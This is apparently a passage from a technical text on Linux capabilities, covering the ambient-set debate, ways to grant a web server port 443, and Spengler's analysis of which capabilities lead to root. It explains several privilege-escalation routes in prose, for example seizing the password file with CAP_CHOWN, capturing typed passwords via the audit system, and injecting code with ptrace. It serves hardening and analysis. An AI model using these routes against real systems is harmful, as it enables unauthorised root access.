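Lameter's patch let an administrator write a list of capability numbers to a system setting. Any process that held one of the listed capabilities would then pass it to every program it ran. Serge Hallyn objected that privilege was supposed to come from both the person and the file, and that this patch ignored the file. He suggested a separate set of capabilities for each process instead, though he was not sure it was a good idea. Lutomirski developed the suggestion into a patch, which went into Linux 4.3 in November 2015.

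The ambient set is normally empty. A process can add a capability to it with the system call `prctl`, without any special privilege, as long as it already has that capability in both its permitted and its inheritable set. The kernel maintains this condition afterwards:

```
every ambient capability is also in (permitted & inheritable)
```

Morgan asked why a capability in the ambient set must also be in the inheritable set, since a process can always copy a capability from its permitted set to its inheritable set. Lutomirski answered that the requirement matters when a process removes a capability. Programs written before 2015 have no code for handling the ambient set. If such a program removes CAP_NET_ADMIN from its permitted or inheritable set, the kernel also removes it from the ambient set, so the program does not pass on a privilege it was written to give up.

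Now suppose that the Chrome OS daemon adds CAP_NET_ADMIN to its ambient set before it runs the unmarked helper:

```
new ambient   = {CAP_NET_ADMIN}
new permitted = {} | {} | {CAP_NET_ADMIN} = {CAP_NET_ADMIN}
new effective = new ambient               = {CAP_NET_ADMIN}
```

The helper starts with the capability switched on, so its code does not have to change. The capability is also in the helper's ambient set, so if the helper is a shell script, the programs it calls get CAP_NET_ADMIN in the same way, and `bash` does not need file capabilities. Capabilities gained through the ambient set do not trigger secure execution, so `LD_PRELOAD` still works.

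Apart from the removals already described, the ambient set becomes empty in these cases:

- The process runs a program that has file capabilities, or one whose setuid or setgid bit changes the process's user or group ID.
- The process gives up root, so that none of its three user IDs is 0 any longer. The securebits flag SECBIT_NO_SETUID_FIXUP turns this rule off.
- The process enters a new user namespace, a boundary within which it can hold capabilities over that namespace's resources only.
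- The process clears the set itself with `prctl`.

A process normally loses its capabilities when it gives up root. This rule protects old programs, many of which start as root, switch to an ordinary user and then run another program that is supposed to have no privileges. To pass on a capability, a launcher must therefore keep its permitted set while it switches users, and add the capability to its ambient set afterwards.

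The rule about privileged programs comes from experience with bugs like the one in sendmail. Lutomirski (2015), in *[PATCH v4 1/2] capabilities*, warns that if an unprivileged user can change a setting that persists into a setuid program, attackers are surprisingly likely to find a use for it. He acknowledges that the rule may be stricter than necessary, because anyone who could exploit a leftover ambient capability already has that capability. But a setuid program might switch to an ordinary user for a risky step and unexpectedly keep CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE. Nobody had shown whether an attacker could exploit that, so he kept the rule as a precaution.

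The rule can also surprise people who use the ambient set. If the daemon runs a copy of `ping` marked `cap_net_raw=ep`, `ping` gets CAP_NET_RAW and loses CAP_NET_ADMIN.

### Morgan's objection

Andrew Morgan, who had written the original Linux specification, formally opposed the patch in March 2015. He called the new behaviour "naive" inheritance because every descendant of a privileged process could get the privilege, even if nobody had prepared it for that. He described the existing scheme as a handshake, in which an ancestor offers a capability and the administrator has marked the descendant's file as ready to receive it. Under this scheme, only programs with file capabilities and programs run by root could exercise privilege.

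He argued that the patch would make some bugs more serious. If a service adds CAP_SYS_ADMIN to its ambient set because one of its helpers needs it, an attacker who can make that service start a shell gets a shell with CAP_SYS_ADMIN. Under the old rules, the shell would have had no capabilities.

Lutomirski replied that an attacker who can run code inside the service does not need the ambient set, since that code can use the service's capabilities directly. This is true of an attacker who exploits a buffer overflow, but not of one who can only make the service start another program. For example, a network daemon might insert the name of a wireless network into a shell command without checking it. Someone nearby could then name a network so that the shell runs part of the name as a separate command. This attacker can choose a program for the daemon to start but cannot otherwise control the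 daemon. The program runs with an ordinary user's rights if the daemon passes on nothing, but gets the capability if the daemon uses the ambient set. Morgan was right that the patch increases the harm from this kind of bug.

Morgan also said that attackers had exploited naive inheritance far more often than faults in the securebits flags, and gave `LD_PRELOAD` and setuid shell scripts as examples. Lutomirski replied, more convincingly, that in both examples a user starts a program that has more privilege than she does and manipulates it. A program that receives ambient capabilities has no more privilege than the process that started it, so the user gains nothing by manipulating it.

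Cook compared the options by asking what an attacker gets from a flaw in a program that the service starts:

| How the service runs | What the attacker gets |
|---|---|
| As root | All of root's power |
| With CAP_NET_ADMIN, passing nothing on | An ordinary user's rights |
| With CAP_NET_ADMIN in its inheritable set | CAP_NET_ADMIN if the flawed program's file allows it, otherwise an ordinary user's rights |
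| With CAP_NET_ADMIN in its ambient set | CAP_NET_ADMIN, in any ordinary program |

On this comparison, the ambient set is riskier than the inheritable set but much safer than root. The relevant comparison depends on what people would otherwise have done. Lameter said that without the change they would run things as root. His own experience supports this, since he had used a private patch for six years and few organisations would go to that trouble. Cook accepted the added risk but wanted the documentation to include "pretty dire warnings", because an attacker can turn almost half of the capabilities into full root. Lutomirski agreed to document this. In his own use, he planned to pass on only CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE and CAP_NET_RAW, and to restrict the programs further with seccomp, which limits the system calls a process can make.

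Morgan objected to forcing the change on everyone, but said he would withdraw his opposition if an administrator could switch the ambient set off for a group of processes and lock that choice. Lameter proposed a simpler control that would let only processes with CAP_SETPCAP add ambient capabilities. Hallyn found this acceptable, but Lutomirski rejected it because a launcher that only had to pass on the right to open a low port would then need a far more powerful capability. Linux 4.3 instead has the kind of switch Morgan asked for, a securebits flag called SECBIT_NO_CAP_AMBIENT_RAISE, with a companion flag that locks it. SECBIT_NO_CAP_AMBIENT_RAISE is off by default, so processes can use the ambient set unless someone turns the flag on.

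### The complaint about Linux 4.3

The day after Linux 4.3 came out, an administrator asked the kernel developers, in *Kernel 4.3 breaks security in systems using capabilities* (Ethgen, 2015), to remove the ambient set. He had replaced setuid on nearly all of his machines' setuid programs with the handshake that Morgan had defended. His example was `mount`, which attaches disks and network drives. Its file had CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE and CAP_SYS_ADMIN in its inheritable set, with the effective bit on, and his login shell had the same two capabilities in its own inheritable set. As with the student administrator's `rm`, the privilege depended on who ran the program. If a flaw in `mount` led it to start an unrelated program, that program got no capabilities.

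Linus Torvalds, who leads kernel development, asked for an actual case in which an existing setup behaved differently. He pointed out that the ambient set stays empty until a process fills it, and that a program that fills it already had the capability. He added that any change in how existing setups behaved would be a bug that the developers should fix.

Ethgen replied that someone who broke into his account could now fill the ambient set, but this is wrong for the settings he posted. His shell had the capabilities only in its inheritable set, and a process must also have them in its permitted set before it can make them ambient. The attacker would first have to take over `mount` while it was running. He could then start a shell that kept both capabilities, which was not possible in this way before. Lutomirski thought this made little difference, because an attacker in that position could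 also make `mount` load a library of his choice, whose code would run with the same capabilities.

Ethgen also objected that the change made administrators depend on programmers. Before 4.3, an administrator who put capabilities on a program knew that its children would not receive them unless he had marked their files. Now that guarantee depended on the program's code, which he had not written and which the next update might change. Ethgen expected careless developers to put every capability they had into the ambient set just to make things work, and thought that nobody would notice until something went wrong. Torvalds's test does not address this complaint, because no existing setup had stopped working.

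Hallyn told him how to get it back, by setting and locking the securebits flags, including the one that disables the ambient set. Ethgen hoped to do this by marking each program file, but a process has to set the flags with `prctl`, for example when the machine starts. Hallyn recommended the full set of flags, which also removes root's automatic privileges and so suits only a system that can run without them. The flag for the ambient set also works on its own, and root then keeps those privileges. Lutomirski warned against changing such settings merely to feel safer, and cited the 2014 bug in which a restricted setuid program failed to give up root.

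Theodore Ts'o, another kernel developer, doubted that requiring a capability in both the process and file inheritable sets could ever work on a general-purpose system. Administrators do much of their work with shell, Perl and Python scripts. To give those scripts privileges, they would have to put practically every capability in the file inheritable sets of the interpreters, and those sets would then no longer keep unvetted code from gaining privileges. Ethgen answered that he wanted to get rid of the setuid programs that ordinary users run, not to have a privileged shell, and that he had a working system for that purpose. Ts'o was describing administrators and services like Lameter's, which cannot avoid scripts.

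Casey Schaufler, who had worked on the POSIX draft, saw the discussion as a sign of a larger failure. He wrote that if Linux had not moved away from root after so many years with capabilities, perhaps it was time to reconsider the plan. Lutomirski suggested that no program should gain privileges at `execve` at all. A user who needed a privileged command would ask a background service to start it, and the service would give the command the privileges it needed. The ambient set suits this design because it lets a parent pass privileges to a child without any marks on files.

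### A web server on port 443

Browsers connect to secure websites on port 443, which is reserved because it is below 1024. Traditionally, a web server starts as root, opens the port and leaves requests to worker processes that run as an ordinary user, though the parent process often keeps running as root. An administrator who wants the whole server to run as the ordinary user `www` has at least four ways to do this, which differ in who else gets the power to open reserved ports.

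She can attach CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE to the server's program file:

```
setcap cap_net_bind_service=ep /usr/local/bin/webserver
```

The server then gets the capability no matter who starts it. Any other user who is allowed to run the file can start a second copy with her own configuration and have it listen on any free port below 1024, where it might pose as the machine's mail server. The administrator can prevent this by allowing only `www` to execute the file. Programs that the server starts do not get the capability unless the server makes it ambient. An update that replaces the file also usually removes the capability, so the server may fail the next time it starts. Because the program runs in secure execution mode, it ignores `LD_LIBRARY_PATH`, which some installations use to locate a program's libraries.

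The ambient set avoids the mark on the file. On most distributions, systemd is the program that starts and supervises services, and it can fill the set according to a service's configuration:

```
[Service]
User=www
ExecStart=/usr/local/bin/webserver
AmbientCapabilities=CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE
CapabilityBoundingSet=CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE
NoNewPrivileges=yes
```

systemd runs as root. It creates a process for the service, switches it to the user `www` while keeping the capability, adds the capability to the ambient set and runs the server. Another user who runs the same file gets nothing, since the privilege comes from the way systemd starts it. The last line turns on `no_new_privs`, which would make a file capability useless but does not affect capabilities the process already has.

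The drawback Morgan described applies here, because every ordinary program that the server starts also gets CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE, including a script that resizes uploaded pictures. An attacker who takes over that script could open other free low ports, though this capability gives no direct way to become root. A server written with capabilities in mind can avoid this by removing the capability from its permitted set after opening port 443. The kernel then removes it from the ambient set too, and the open port keeps working.

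The server does not need a capability at all if another process opens the port for it. systemd can open a socket (the endpoint of a network connection) on port 443 and pass the server a file descriptor for it:

```
[Socket]
ListenStream=443
```

The server can now accept connections on port 443 and cannot open any other reserved port. This is the narrowest of the four grants, because the descriptor is an object capability for one socket. systemd also keeps the socket open while the server restarts, so no other program can take the port. If the server leaks the descriptor to a program it starts, that program can accept visitors' connections but cannot open port 25.

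The server's code has to support this by looking for a socket it has received instead of opening its own. `authbind`, a tool from 1998, works with programs that lack this support. It uses `LD_PRELOAD` to replace the function that claims a port with one that passes the program's socket to a small setuid-root helper. The helper checks that the administrator has allowed this user to have this port, claims it and exits. The web server never has any privilege, but the machine has one more setuid-root program that must be free of mistakes.

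Finally, the administrator can change which ports are reserved:

```
sysctl net.ipv4.ip_unprivileged_port_start=443
```

After this change, no program needs a capability to open port 443, so there is none to steal or leak. But every user on the machine can now open any port from 443 upwards, including those that mail programs use for encrypted connections. If the web server stops for a moment, another user's program can take over port 443. Browsers would normally warn visitors, because the impostor lacks the private key for the site's certificate. However, some certificate authorities issue a certificate to whoever can answer a test on port 443, so an impostor who holds the port for long enough might get a valid one. If a machine or container runs only the web server, there may be no other users to worry about, which would make this a reasonable choice.

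### When the server is a Python script

Suppose the web server is a file named `server.py`. The kernel cannot run this file directly, so it reads the interpreter's name from the first line and runs Python, which then reads the script. As Lutomirski notes in his patch, the kernel uses the capabilities on the interpreter's file, not those on the script. An administrator can attach CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE to `server.py` without an error, but the server still cannot open port 443.

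She may then be tempted to attach the capability to Python itself:

```
setcap cap_net_bind_service=ep /usr/bin/python3.12
```

Now the server works, but every other Python script on the machine can also bind to a low port. An administrator cannot vet Python as she can `ping`, because what Python does depends on the script, and any user can write one. CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE limits the damage to ports. If she gave Python CAP_SETUID in the same way, any user could become root with a one-line script.

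Marking the interpreter `cap_net_bind_service=ei` is safer, since only processes with the capability in their inheritable set would be able to use it. But if she sets this up for `www`, all of that user's Python scripts can open low ports, not just the server. She could also attach the capability to a private copy of Python that only `www` may run. She would then have to update the copy whenever Python has a security fix, and `www` could still use it to run any script.

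The methods that don't mark a file have none of these problems. systemd can start `server.py` with an ambient capability, which only that Python process and the processes it starts receive. Or systemd can open port 443 and pass the socket to the script, which then needs no privilege.

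## When one capability is as good as root

CAP_SETUID looks much like CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE in a configuration file, but it lets a process change its user ID to 0 and then run another program, which receives every capability because it runs as root. If an administrator replaces root with CAP_SETUID, the process starts with only one of the 41 capabilities, but an attacker who controls it can regain the other 40 this way.

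A capability is root-equivalent if an attacker who can run arbitrary code in a process that holds it can normally obtain all the others. CAP_SETUID is one such capability. The definition assumes that the process runs as an ordinary user with no other capabilities, on a system without extra confinement such as namespaces, SELinux (a set of mandatory access rules) or securebits flags that remove root's automatic privileges.

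The process has to run as an ordinary user because user ID 0 alone is enough to regain root's power. Brad Spengler, who develops the grsecurity patches for the Linux kernel, explained in *False Boundaries and Arbitrary Code Execution* in early 2011 that a root process that has dropped its capabilities still owns the system's files, including the device file that gives direct access to the disk, and normally regains every capability when it runs another program. A service that starts as root and gives up a few capabilities therefore gains little protection until it also changes its user ID.

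libcap's *Notes concerning wider use of capabilities* suggest giving the system's files to a user who cannot log in, so that root without capabilities would have no special rights over them. Someone proposed the same thing in the discussion under LWN's notice of Spengler's post, *Spengler* (2011). Another reader answered that many Unix programs had once belonged to a user called `bin`, and that "gaining user 'bin' was another way to root the box". An attacker who controls the files that root runs does not need root's user ID.

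### Spengler's argument

Spengler's case against many of the capabilities has five steps:

1. Administrators give a program capabilities instead of root so that an attacker who takes it over can do less damage.
2. The program may have a bug that lets an attacker run code of their choice inside it.
3. That code can use the program's capabilities for anything the kernel allows, whatever the programmer had in mind.
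4. For some capabilities, the kernel allows something that leads to full root power.
5. An attacker who takes over a program with one of these capabilities can therefore do as much damage as if it had been running as root.

A capability can allow a program to do more than the program uses it for, which is easy to overlook. For example, `cron`, which runs scheduled jobs, uses CAP_SETUID to run each user's jobs under that user's ID. But the kernel lets `cron` switch to any ID at any time, including 0, which is root's.

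Each capability has to be checked individually to see whether it leads to full root power. Linux had 35 capabilities at the time, and Spengler's page now describes a route to root for 19 of them. He labels 16 of the routes "generic", meaning they should work on most systems. The other three, for CAP_FSETID, CAP_SETGID and CAP_IPC_OWNER, are "situational". He lists CAP_KILL, CAP_NET_ADMIN and CAP_NET_RAW separately as very likely to lead to root in practice, and knew of no route for the remaining 13. The list does not cover the six capabilities added since.

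Other reports give different totals because Spengler kept revising the page as readers wrote to him. His first version had 15. On 3 January 2011, *Capabilities systems considered harmful* (dave, 2011) quoted a total of 18, and two days later LWN reported 20. Spengler then moved the attacks that rely on impersonating a network service into the separate group, because SSH, the usual program for remote logins, warns users when they connect to an impostor. That brought the total back to 18, and it later rose to 19.

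### Five kinds of route

The 19 routes fall into five groups according to what the attacker gains control of:

| Kind of route | Capabilities |
|---|---|
| Changing files that root trusts | CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE, CAP_CHOWN, CAP_FOWNER, CAP_FSETID, CAP_SETGID, CAP_MKNOD, CAP_SYS_CHROOT, CAP_SYS_ADMIN |
| Becoming another user | CAP_SETUID, CAP_DAC_READ_SEARCH, CAP_AUDIT_CONTROL |
| Controlling another process | CAP_SYS_PTRACE, CAP_SYS_TTY_CONFIG, CAP_IPC_OWNER |
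| Altering the kernel | CAP_SYS_MODULE, CAP_SYS_BOOT, CAP_SYS_RAWIO |
| Granting oneself more capabilities | CAP_SETFCAP, CAP_SETPCAP |

Some capabilities belong in more than one group. CAP_SYS_ADMIN, which covers dozens of unrelated operations, lets an attacker mount a different file over a system program or insert commands into an administrator's terminal.

CAP_CHOWN gives an attacker a simple way to change files that root trusts. It lets a process change the owner of any file, so the attacker can take ownership of the password file, replace root's password and log in as root.

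An attacker with CAP_AUDIT_CONTROL can also become root by learning root's password. The capability lets a process configure the kernel's audit system, which can record what people type at their terminals. The attacker turns on the recording and waits for an administrator to type the password.

CAP_SYS_PTRACE exists for debuggers, which need to inspect and change the memory of running programs. An attacker can use it to run their own code inside a process that has every capability.

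CAP_SYS_MODULE lets a process load code into the kernel. Since the kernel performs all the permission checks, code running inside it can ignore them or switch them off.

With CAP_SETFCAP, an attacker can attach every capability to a program of their own and run it.

Spengler's other example of attackers granting themselves more capabilities, CAP_SETPCAP, is doubtful. He calls the route generic because a process with CAP_SETPCAP can add any capability in its bounding set to its inheritable set, then pass it to the programs it starts. But almost no program files allow this. The attacker cannot use the ambient set instead, because a capability must already be in the permitted set to be added there, and CAP_SETPCAP adds nothing to the permitted set.

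More plausibly, an attacker could use CAP_SETPCAP to remove CAP_SETUID from the bounding set, then start an old setuid-root program, which might fail to give up root, as sendmail did in 2000. This works only if a program with that weakness is installed, so CAP_SETPCAP seems to belong with the situational cases.

### The services on Spengler's machine

A root-equivalent capability matters little if few programs need one. Spengler therefore listed the services on one of his own machines that needed any capability after they had started. There were nine:

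| Service | What it does | Capabilities needed after startup |
|---|---|---|
| `syslogd` | Keeps system logs | CAP_SYS_ADMIN, CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE, CAP_DAC_READ_SEARCH |
| `cron` | Runs scheduled jobs | CAP_SETUID, CAP_SETGID |
| `login` | Logs users in | CAP_SETUID, CAP_SETGID, CAP_FSETID, CAP_CHOWN |
| `cvs` | Stores versions of source code | CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE, CAP_SETUID, CAP_FSETID |
| `postfix` | Delivers mail | CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE, CAP_KILL, CAP_SETUID, CAP_SETGID, CAP_SYS_CHROOT |
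| `apache` | Serves web pages | CAP_KILL, CAP_SETUID, CAP_SETGID |
| `sshd` | Accepts remote logins | CAP_KILL, CAP_SYS_TTY_CONFIG, CAP_SETUID, CAP_SETGID, CAP_CHOWN |
| `xinetd` | Starts other network services | CAP_SETUID, CAP_SETGID |
| `procmail` | Sorts mail | CAP_SETUID, CAP_SETGID, CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE |

All nine programs needed at least one root-equivalent capability. Eight needed CAP_SETUID, because their work includes acting for different users. A program that can act as any user can act as root, so a more careful choice of capabilities would not have helped these eight much.

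Spengler looked at only one machine and left out programs that an administrator runs briefly. He also notes that the part of a service exposed to the network may not have the dangerous capability. A well-designed login server handles messages from strangers in an unprivileged process and keeps its privileges in a separate one. An attacker who takes over the exposed process needs a second bug to take over the privileged one.

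Later measurements of `sshd` agree with Spengler's entry. *PrivAnalyzer* (Criswell, Zhou and colleagues, 2019) counted the instructions that five programs executed while holding each combination of capabilities. `sshd` kept CAP_SETUID, CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE and five others for more than 99% of its run, although limitations of the tool that decided when it could safely drop them probably explain part of this. `ping` dropped all its capabilities almost at once, and a small web server held none for 90% of its run.

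Criswell and colleagues also tested what an attacker could do with each combination. They modeled the relevant Linux system calls and used a program to search for sequences of calls that led to one of four results: reading the machine's memory through a device file, writing to that memory, opening a reserved port or stopping another user's server. CAP_SETUID alone was enough for all of these except opening a port. CAP_SETGID alone allowed only reading the memory, and CAP_NET_RAW together with CAP_NET_ADMIN allowed none of the four.

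According to the manual, opening this device file requires CAP_SYS_RAWIO, but the model seems to omit that check. Its results are therefore better evidence about root-owned files in general than about memory. The model also leaves out `execve`, so it does not cover the shortest route from CAP_SETUID to root.

The researchers rewrote `passwd` so that an attacker could read and write the memory device during only 4% of its run, down from 97%. As part of the change, they created a new user, `etc`, to own the `/etc` directory and the password file, and `passwd` ran as that user, without capabilities, for the remaining 96%. An attacker who took over `passwd` during that time could still replace root's password, because `etc` owns the file. The model did not include this attack, so the program counted as safe. The LWN reader's objection to the user `bin` applies here too.

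In *Decap*, Hasan, Ghavamnia and Polychronakis (2022) examined many more programs, 201 setuid programs from Ubuntu 18.04, but used a different standard. They looked for the capabilities each program could do without. Their tool removed CAP_SYS_ADMIN from 69% of the programs, which they regard as the decisive improvement because they consider that capability basically equivalent to root. On this basis, they count 612 of 869 known privilege-escalation vulnerabilities as mitigated.

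By Spengler's standard, none of the 201 programs fell below root-equivalence, because the tool left all of them with CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE, CAP_DAC_READ_SEARCH and CAP_FOWNER. An attacker who took over the reduced `passwd` could not mount a file system but could still rewrite the password file. Removing CAP_SYS_ADMIN is therefore not enough to mitigate a vulnerability if the attacker still has CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE. However, the tool overestimates what programs need. It gives CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE to any program that opens files, and it gives `ping` 16 capabilities when `ping` can work with one. The study therefore does not show that all these programs need root-equivalent capabilities.

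### Reading without writing

CAP_DAC_READ_SEARCH, the capability that suits a backup program, lets a process read every file but not change any. Spengler counts it as root-equivalent because some files, such as the password file and the private keys root uses for remote logins, contain information that a process could use to become root.

The attacker's success depends on what the files contain. The password file stores passwords in scrambled form, so the attacker has to guess a password, scramble it the same way and compare the results. This works against a weak password but not a long random one. Some machines have no root password, and their administrators log in with keys kept on other computers. Reading every file on such a machine might not give the attacker root, so "generic" seems too strong for this capability.

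The attacker could still copy every user's mail, the customer database and the web server's private key. For many organisations this would be as bad as losing control of the machine. Root-equivalence means only that an attacker can use a capability to obtain the others, so a capability that is not root-equivalent can still be very dangerous.

CAP_SETGID raises a similar problem because it lets a process join any group. On the Ubuntu system that Criswell and colleagues used, the password file belonged to the `shadow` group, whose members can normally read it. Spengler mentions another group, `staff`, whose members could replace programs in `/usr/local` on Debian-based systems. Since the system usually looks for programs there first, root might run the replacement. The power of CAP_SETGID therefore depends on which groups a distribution has created and what their members can do.

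### Capabilities that gain force together

Spengler knew of no way to turn CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE into root. He had once thought that a process could use it to take over traffic to a port that another service was already using, but he later withdrew the claim. libcap's notes still call it "a formidable privilege", because a process could open the port of a login service, imitate the login screen and collect passwords. This works only if the port is free, and on most machines the real service is using it.

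CAP_KILL removes this obstacle, because an attacker with both capabilities can stop the genuine service and start an imitation on the same port. With CAP_KILL alone, the attacker could do this only to services on ports that are not reserved. Even with both, the attack works only if someone connects, ignores any warning and types a useful password. Spengler therefore treats the combination as a likely but not certain route to root.

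An attacker with CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE can become root faster if they also have CAP_FSETID. With CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE alone, they can alter an ordinary system program, but must then wait for root to run it. Altering a setuid-root program would be quicker, because the attacker could run it immediately. But the kernel clears the setuid bit when a process changes the file, unless that process also has CAP_FSETID.

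The IEEE group had wanted administrators to be confident that the capabilities they granted would not combine to provide one they had withheld. Assessing capabilities one at a time, as Spengler's list does, cannot establish that. Sixteen of the 35 capabilities were not on his list, which makes 120 possible pairs, and he describes only one that becomes more powerful in combination. Nobody seems to have checked the rest systematically.

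Other readers suggested less direct uses for capabilities that Spengler could not turn into root. With CAP_SYS_NICE, a process can control which processor another program runs on and how much time it gets. This could help an attacker infer secret keys from the program's timing, or exploit a bug that appears only when two events happen in a particular order. With CAP_LINUX_IMMUTABLE, an attacker could make a file unchangeable so that a firewall setup script fails unnoticed. None of these suggestions amounts to a route to root, but they are a reason not to assume that "no known route" means no route exists.

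### When the answer depends on other programs

CAP_IPC_OWNER lets a process bypass the permission checks in System V IPC, an old set of facilities that programs use to share memory and exchange messages. If a program running as root keeps data in shared memory and trusts it, an attacker with this capability could change the data and perhaps take over the program. If no privileged program on the machine uses these facilities, an attacker can't use the capability to become root.

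An administrator therefore cannot tell from the manual's description of CAP_IPC_OWNER whether it is as good as root. She has to know what else is running, and the answer may change when she installs another package.

### Bugs that give an attacker less than full control

The LWN discussion turned to Spengler's assumption that the attacker can run any code they like. Many bugs don't allow that. One reader described a service that runs as the unprivileged user `nobody` with CAP_SETUID and handles temporary files carelessly, so that an attacker can choose which file it writes to. If the service ran as root, the attacker could overwrite the password file. With only CAP_SETUID, the write fails, because the service is still running as `nobody` and the bug doesn't let the attacker make it change its user ID.

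If the process had CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE, the kernel would allow the write. When a bug lets an attacker trigger only certain operations, limiting the process to a root-equivalent capability protects the system only if that capability does not permit those operations.

Replacing root with CAP_SETUID also helps against bugs that only let an attacker start another program, which Morgan raised in the debate over the ambient set. The attacker gets an ordinary user's rights instead of a root shell, unless the service has made the capability ambient.

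drag (2011), in *Spengler*, replied that full control was the whole point, since Fedora and Ubuntu were replacing setuid programs precisely to limit what an attacker could do after exploiting one. The developer of PaX, a set of protections against memory attacks that forms part of grsecurity, added that an attacker with less control can do less under either system. This is true, but it does not answer the temporary-file example, in which the same bug gives the attacker the password file under root and nothing under CAP_SETUID.

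The objection is sound, but its importance depends on how many bugs are limited in this way. The reader who gave the example conceded that running arbitrary code is probably the most common result of a security hole, because a program that has started to misbehave tends to break more of its own assumptions. Another reader suggested, only for the sake of argument, that capabilities might make 1% of bugs harmless. Researchers generally plan for the worse case. Criswell et al. and Hasan et al. assume an attacker who can use any capability in the permitted set, and so does *KubeCap* (2026) for attackers who can run code inside a container.

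Spengler did not conclude that people should go back to root. He pointed out that privileged programs do not normally perform the operations on his list, so an attacker has to make the program do something it was not written to do. If the system prevents this, a capability limits the attacker much more effectively. PaX was meant to help by stopping attackers from introducing new code. But attackers can also reuse code already in a program's memory, and Spengler acknowledged that nobody yet had complete protection against that.

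One reader dismissed the post as an attempt to scare people into using grsecurity and complained that it contained no real case of misuse. Spengler did have an interest in the conclusion, but readers can check his list against the manual, which describes most of the powers involved.

### Accidents, delays and local conditions

Capabilities can also prevent mistakes, even when they would not stop an attacker. giraffedata (2012), in *CAP_SYS_ADMIN*, wrote that he used them mainly to keep a process from accidentally using a privilege he had never meant it to have. He found it extremely useful that a process could not update someone else's file even if it could change its user ID to the owner's. If a mistake in a file name led a program to try to write to someone else's file, the write would fail, because the program would not first change its ID as an attacker would.

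Spengler's argument does not undermine this benefit. But another LWN reader pointed out that some people rely on capabilities for more than this. Linux-VServer, an early system for running several isolated servers on one machine, used them to keep each server's users from gaining control of the host. Its administrators needed to know which capabilities would let those users obtain the other capabilities.

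Other critics said that many of the routes were slow or worked only on some machines. One contrasted a script that gives an attacker root immediately with a trap that might take two days to capture a password, or never capture one. Spengler replied that attackers do not mind waiting a few days, and that one person can publish a tool that makes a complicated attack easy for everyone else. The critic answered that no tool can make an administrator type a password. Matthew Garrett, posting on LWN as mjg59, added that recording passwords is useless on a machine where people log in only with keys, whereas a compromised service running as root is always serious.

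The critics are right about CAP_AUDIT_CONTROL and several other capabilities on the list, but their objection does not apply to CAP_SETUID, CAP_SETFCAP or CAP_SYS_MODULE, which normally work immediately and without anyone else's involvement. The objection therefore does little to show that the services on Spengler's machine were safe, since eight of the nine needed CAP_SETUID.

Restricting a process's view of the file system does not necessarily help either. unBrice (2011), in *Spengler*, suggested that CAP_SETUID might be reasonable for a process confined with `chroot`, which makes one directory look like the whole file system. Spengler replied that the process could change to another user's ID and take control of that user's processes outside the directory.

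### What later kernels changed

Kernel developers have closed or narrowed several routes to root that depended on another feature of the system. From August 2009 to March 2011, a process with CAP_NET_ADMIN could load any kernel module from the standard directories, including modules unrelated to networking. This gave attackers much more kernel code to search for bugs. According to Spengler, later kernels do not allow this.

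The route from CAP_SYS_CHROOT to root has also become harder. The attacker had to give a setuid-root program a second name, called a hard link, in a directory that held an altered system library. Running the program with that directory as its whole file system made it load the altered library as root. Since version 3.6, Linux has had a setting that stops users from making hard links to other people's setuid programs, and most distributions turn it on.

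Lockdown mode, an optional feature added in Linux 5.4, limits how CAP_SYS_MODULE, CAP_SYS_BOOT and CAP_SYS_RAWIO can be used to take control of the kernel. When it is on, even root cannot load a module without a trusted signature, start an unsigned replacement kernel or access hardware ports directly. Lockdown protects the kernel from root, but it does not stop anyone from becoming root.

New features can also create ways to escalate privileges. Linux 4.14 added namespaced file capabilities, which let a root process get around its lack of CAP_SETFCAP. The process could create a user namespace with the same root user, attach capabilities to a file there and use them outside the namespace. Since Linux 5.12, a process has needed CAP_SETFCAP to map user ID 0 into a new user namespace, which prevents this.

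The most direct ways to get full root access from a single capability still work on an ordinary system. According to the current manual, CAP_SETUID lets a process change its user IDs at will, CAP_CHOWN lets it change the owner of any file, and CAP_SYS_PTRACE lets it trace any process. The capabilities exist to grant these powers, so kernel developers cannot remove the powers without breaking the programs that need them.

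An administrator can sometimes limit a capability to particular targets. SafeSetID, an optional feature added in Linux 5.1, lets her list the user IDs that a given user's processes may switch to. If a service acts only for three ordinary users, she can leave root off its list so that the service can't use CAP_SETUID to switch directly to user ID 0. This would not work for `cron` on most machines, because `cron` also has to run root's jobs.

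## How CAP_SYS_ADMIN became a catch-all

SafeSetID can limit CAP_SETUID to a list of users because almost everything that capability allows concerns user IDs. No single list of targets could limit CAP_SYS_ADMIN in the same way, because it allows unrelated operations such as mounting a disk, renaming the machine, setting up a container and sending privileged commands to many device drivers.

### What the capability allows

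The entry for CAP_SYS_ADMIN in the Linux man-pages has 31 items, and the page calls this a partial list. The table groups some of them by subject.

| Subject | Some operations that need CAP_SYS_ADMIN |
|---|---|
| File systems and storage | Mounting and unmounting file systems, turning swap space on and off, managing disk quotas |
| The machine's identity | Setting the host name and domain name |
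| Namespaces | Creating most kinds of namespace (separate views of system resources, used to build containers) and entering existing ones |
| Devices | Administering many device drivers, changing which devices a group of processes may use, inserting characters into another terminal's input |
| Other processes | Deleting other users' System V shared memory, giving a false process ID to another program, suspending the seccomp restrictions on a program being debugged |
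| Limits | Exceeding the system-wide limit on open files or the limit on a user's processes |

The kernel checks the same bit for every operation in the table. Suppose a program's only privileged task is to set the host name when the machine starts. An attacker could do little harm with that power alone. But setting the host name requires CAP_SYS_ADMIN, so an attacker who takes over the program can also mount a file system over `/etc` and then become root.

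Other capabilities also permit some of the operations that CAP_SYS_ADMIN permits. For example, either CAP_SYS_ADMIN or CAP_SYS_RESOURCE lets a process exceed the limit on how many processes a user can run. An administrator who grants only CAP_SYS_ADMIN therefore still allows the process to exceed that limit. The IEEE group had wanted to avoid this kind of overlap.

The items about devices are open-ended. Programs control devices through the system call `ioctl`, and each driver's author decides which commands it accepts and which of them need privilege, so the manual can only list them as "administrative operations on many device drivers". An administrator would have to read the code of a machine's drivers to find out exactly what CAP_SYS_ADMIN allows on it.

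### Counting the checks

In *CAP_SYS_ADMIN* (2012), Michael Kerrisk measured how much of the kernel depended on this one capability. Kerrisk, who talked to kernel developers while writing manual pages for new kernel features, ran a script to count the places in the kernel's C files that used each capability.

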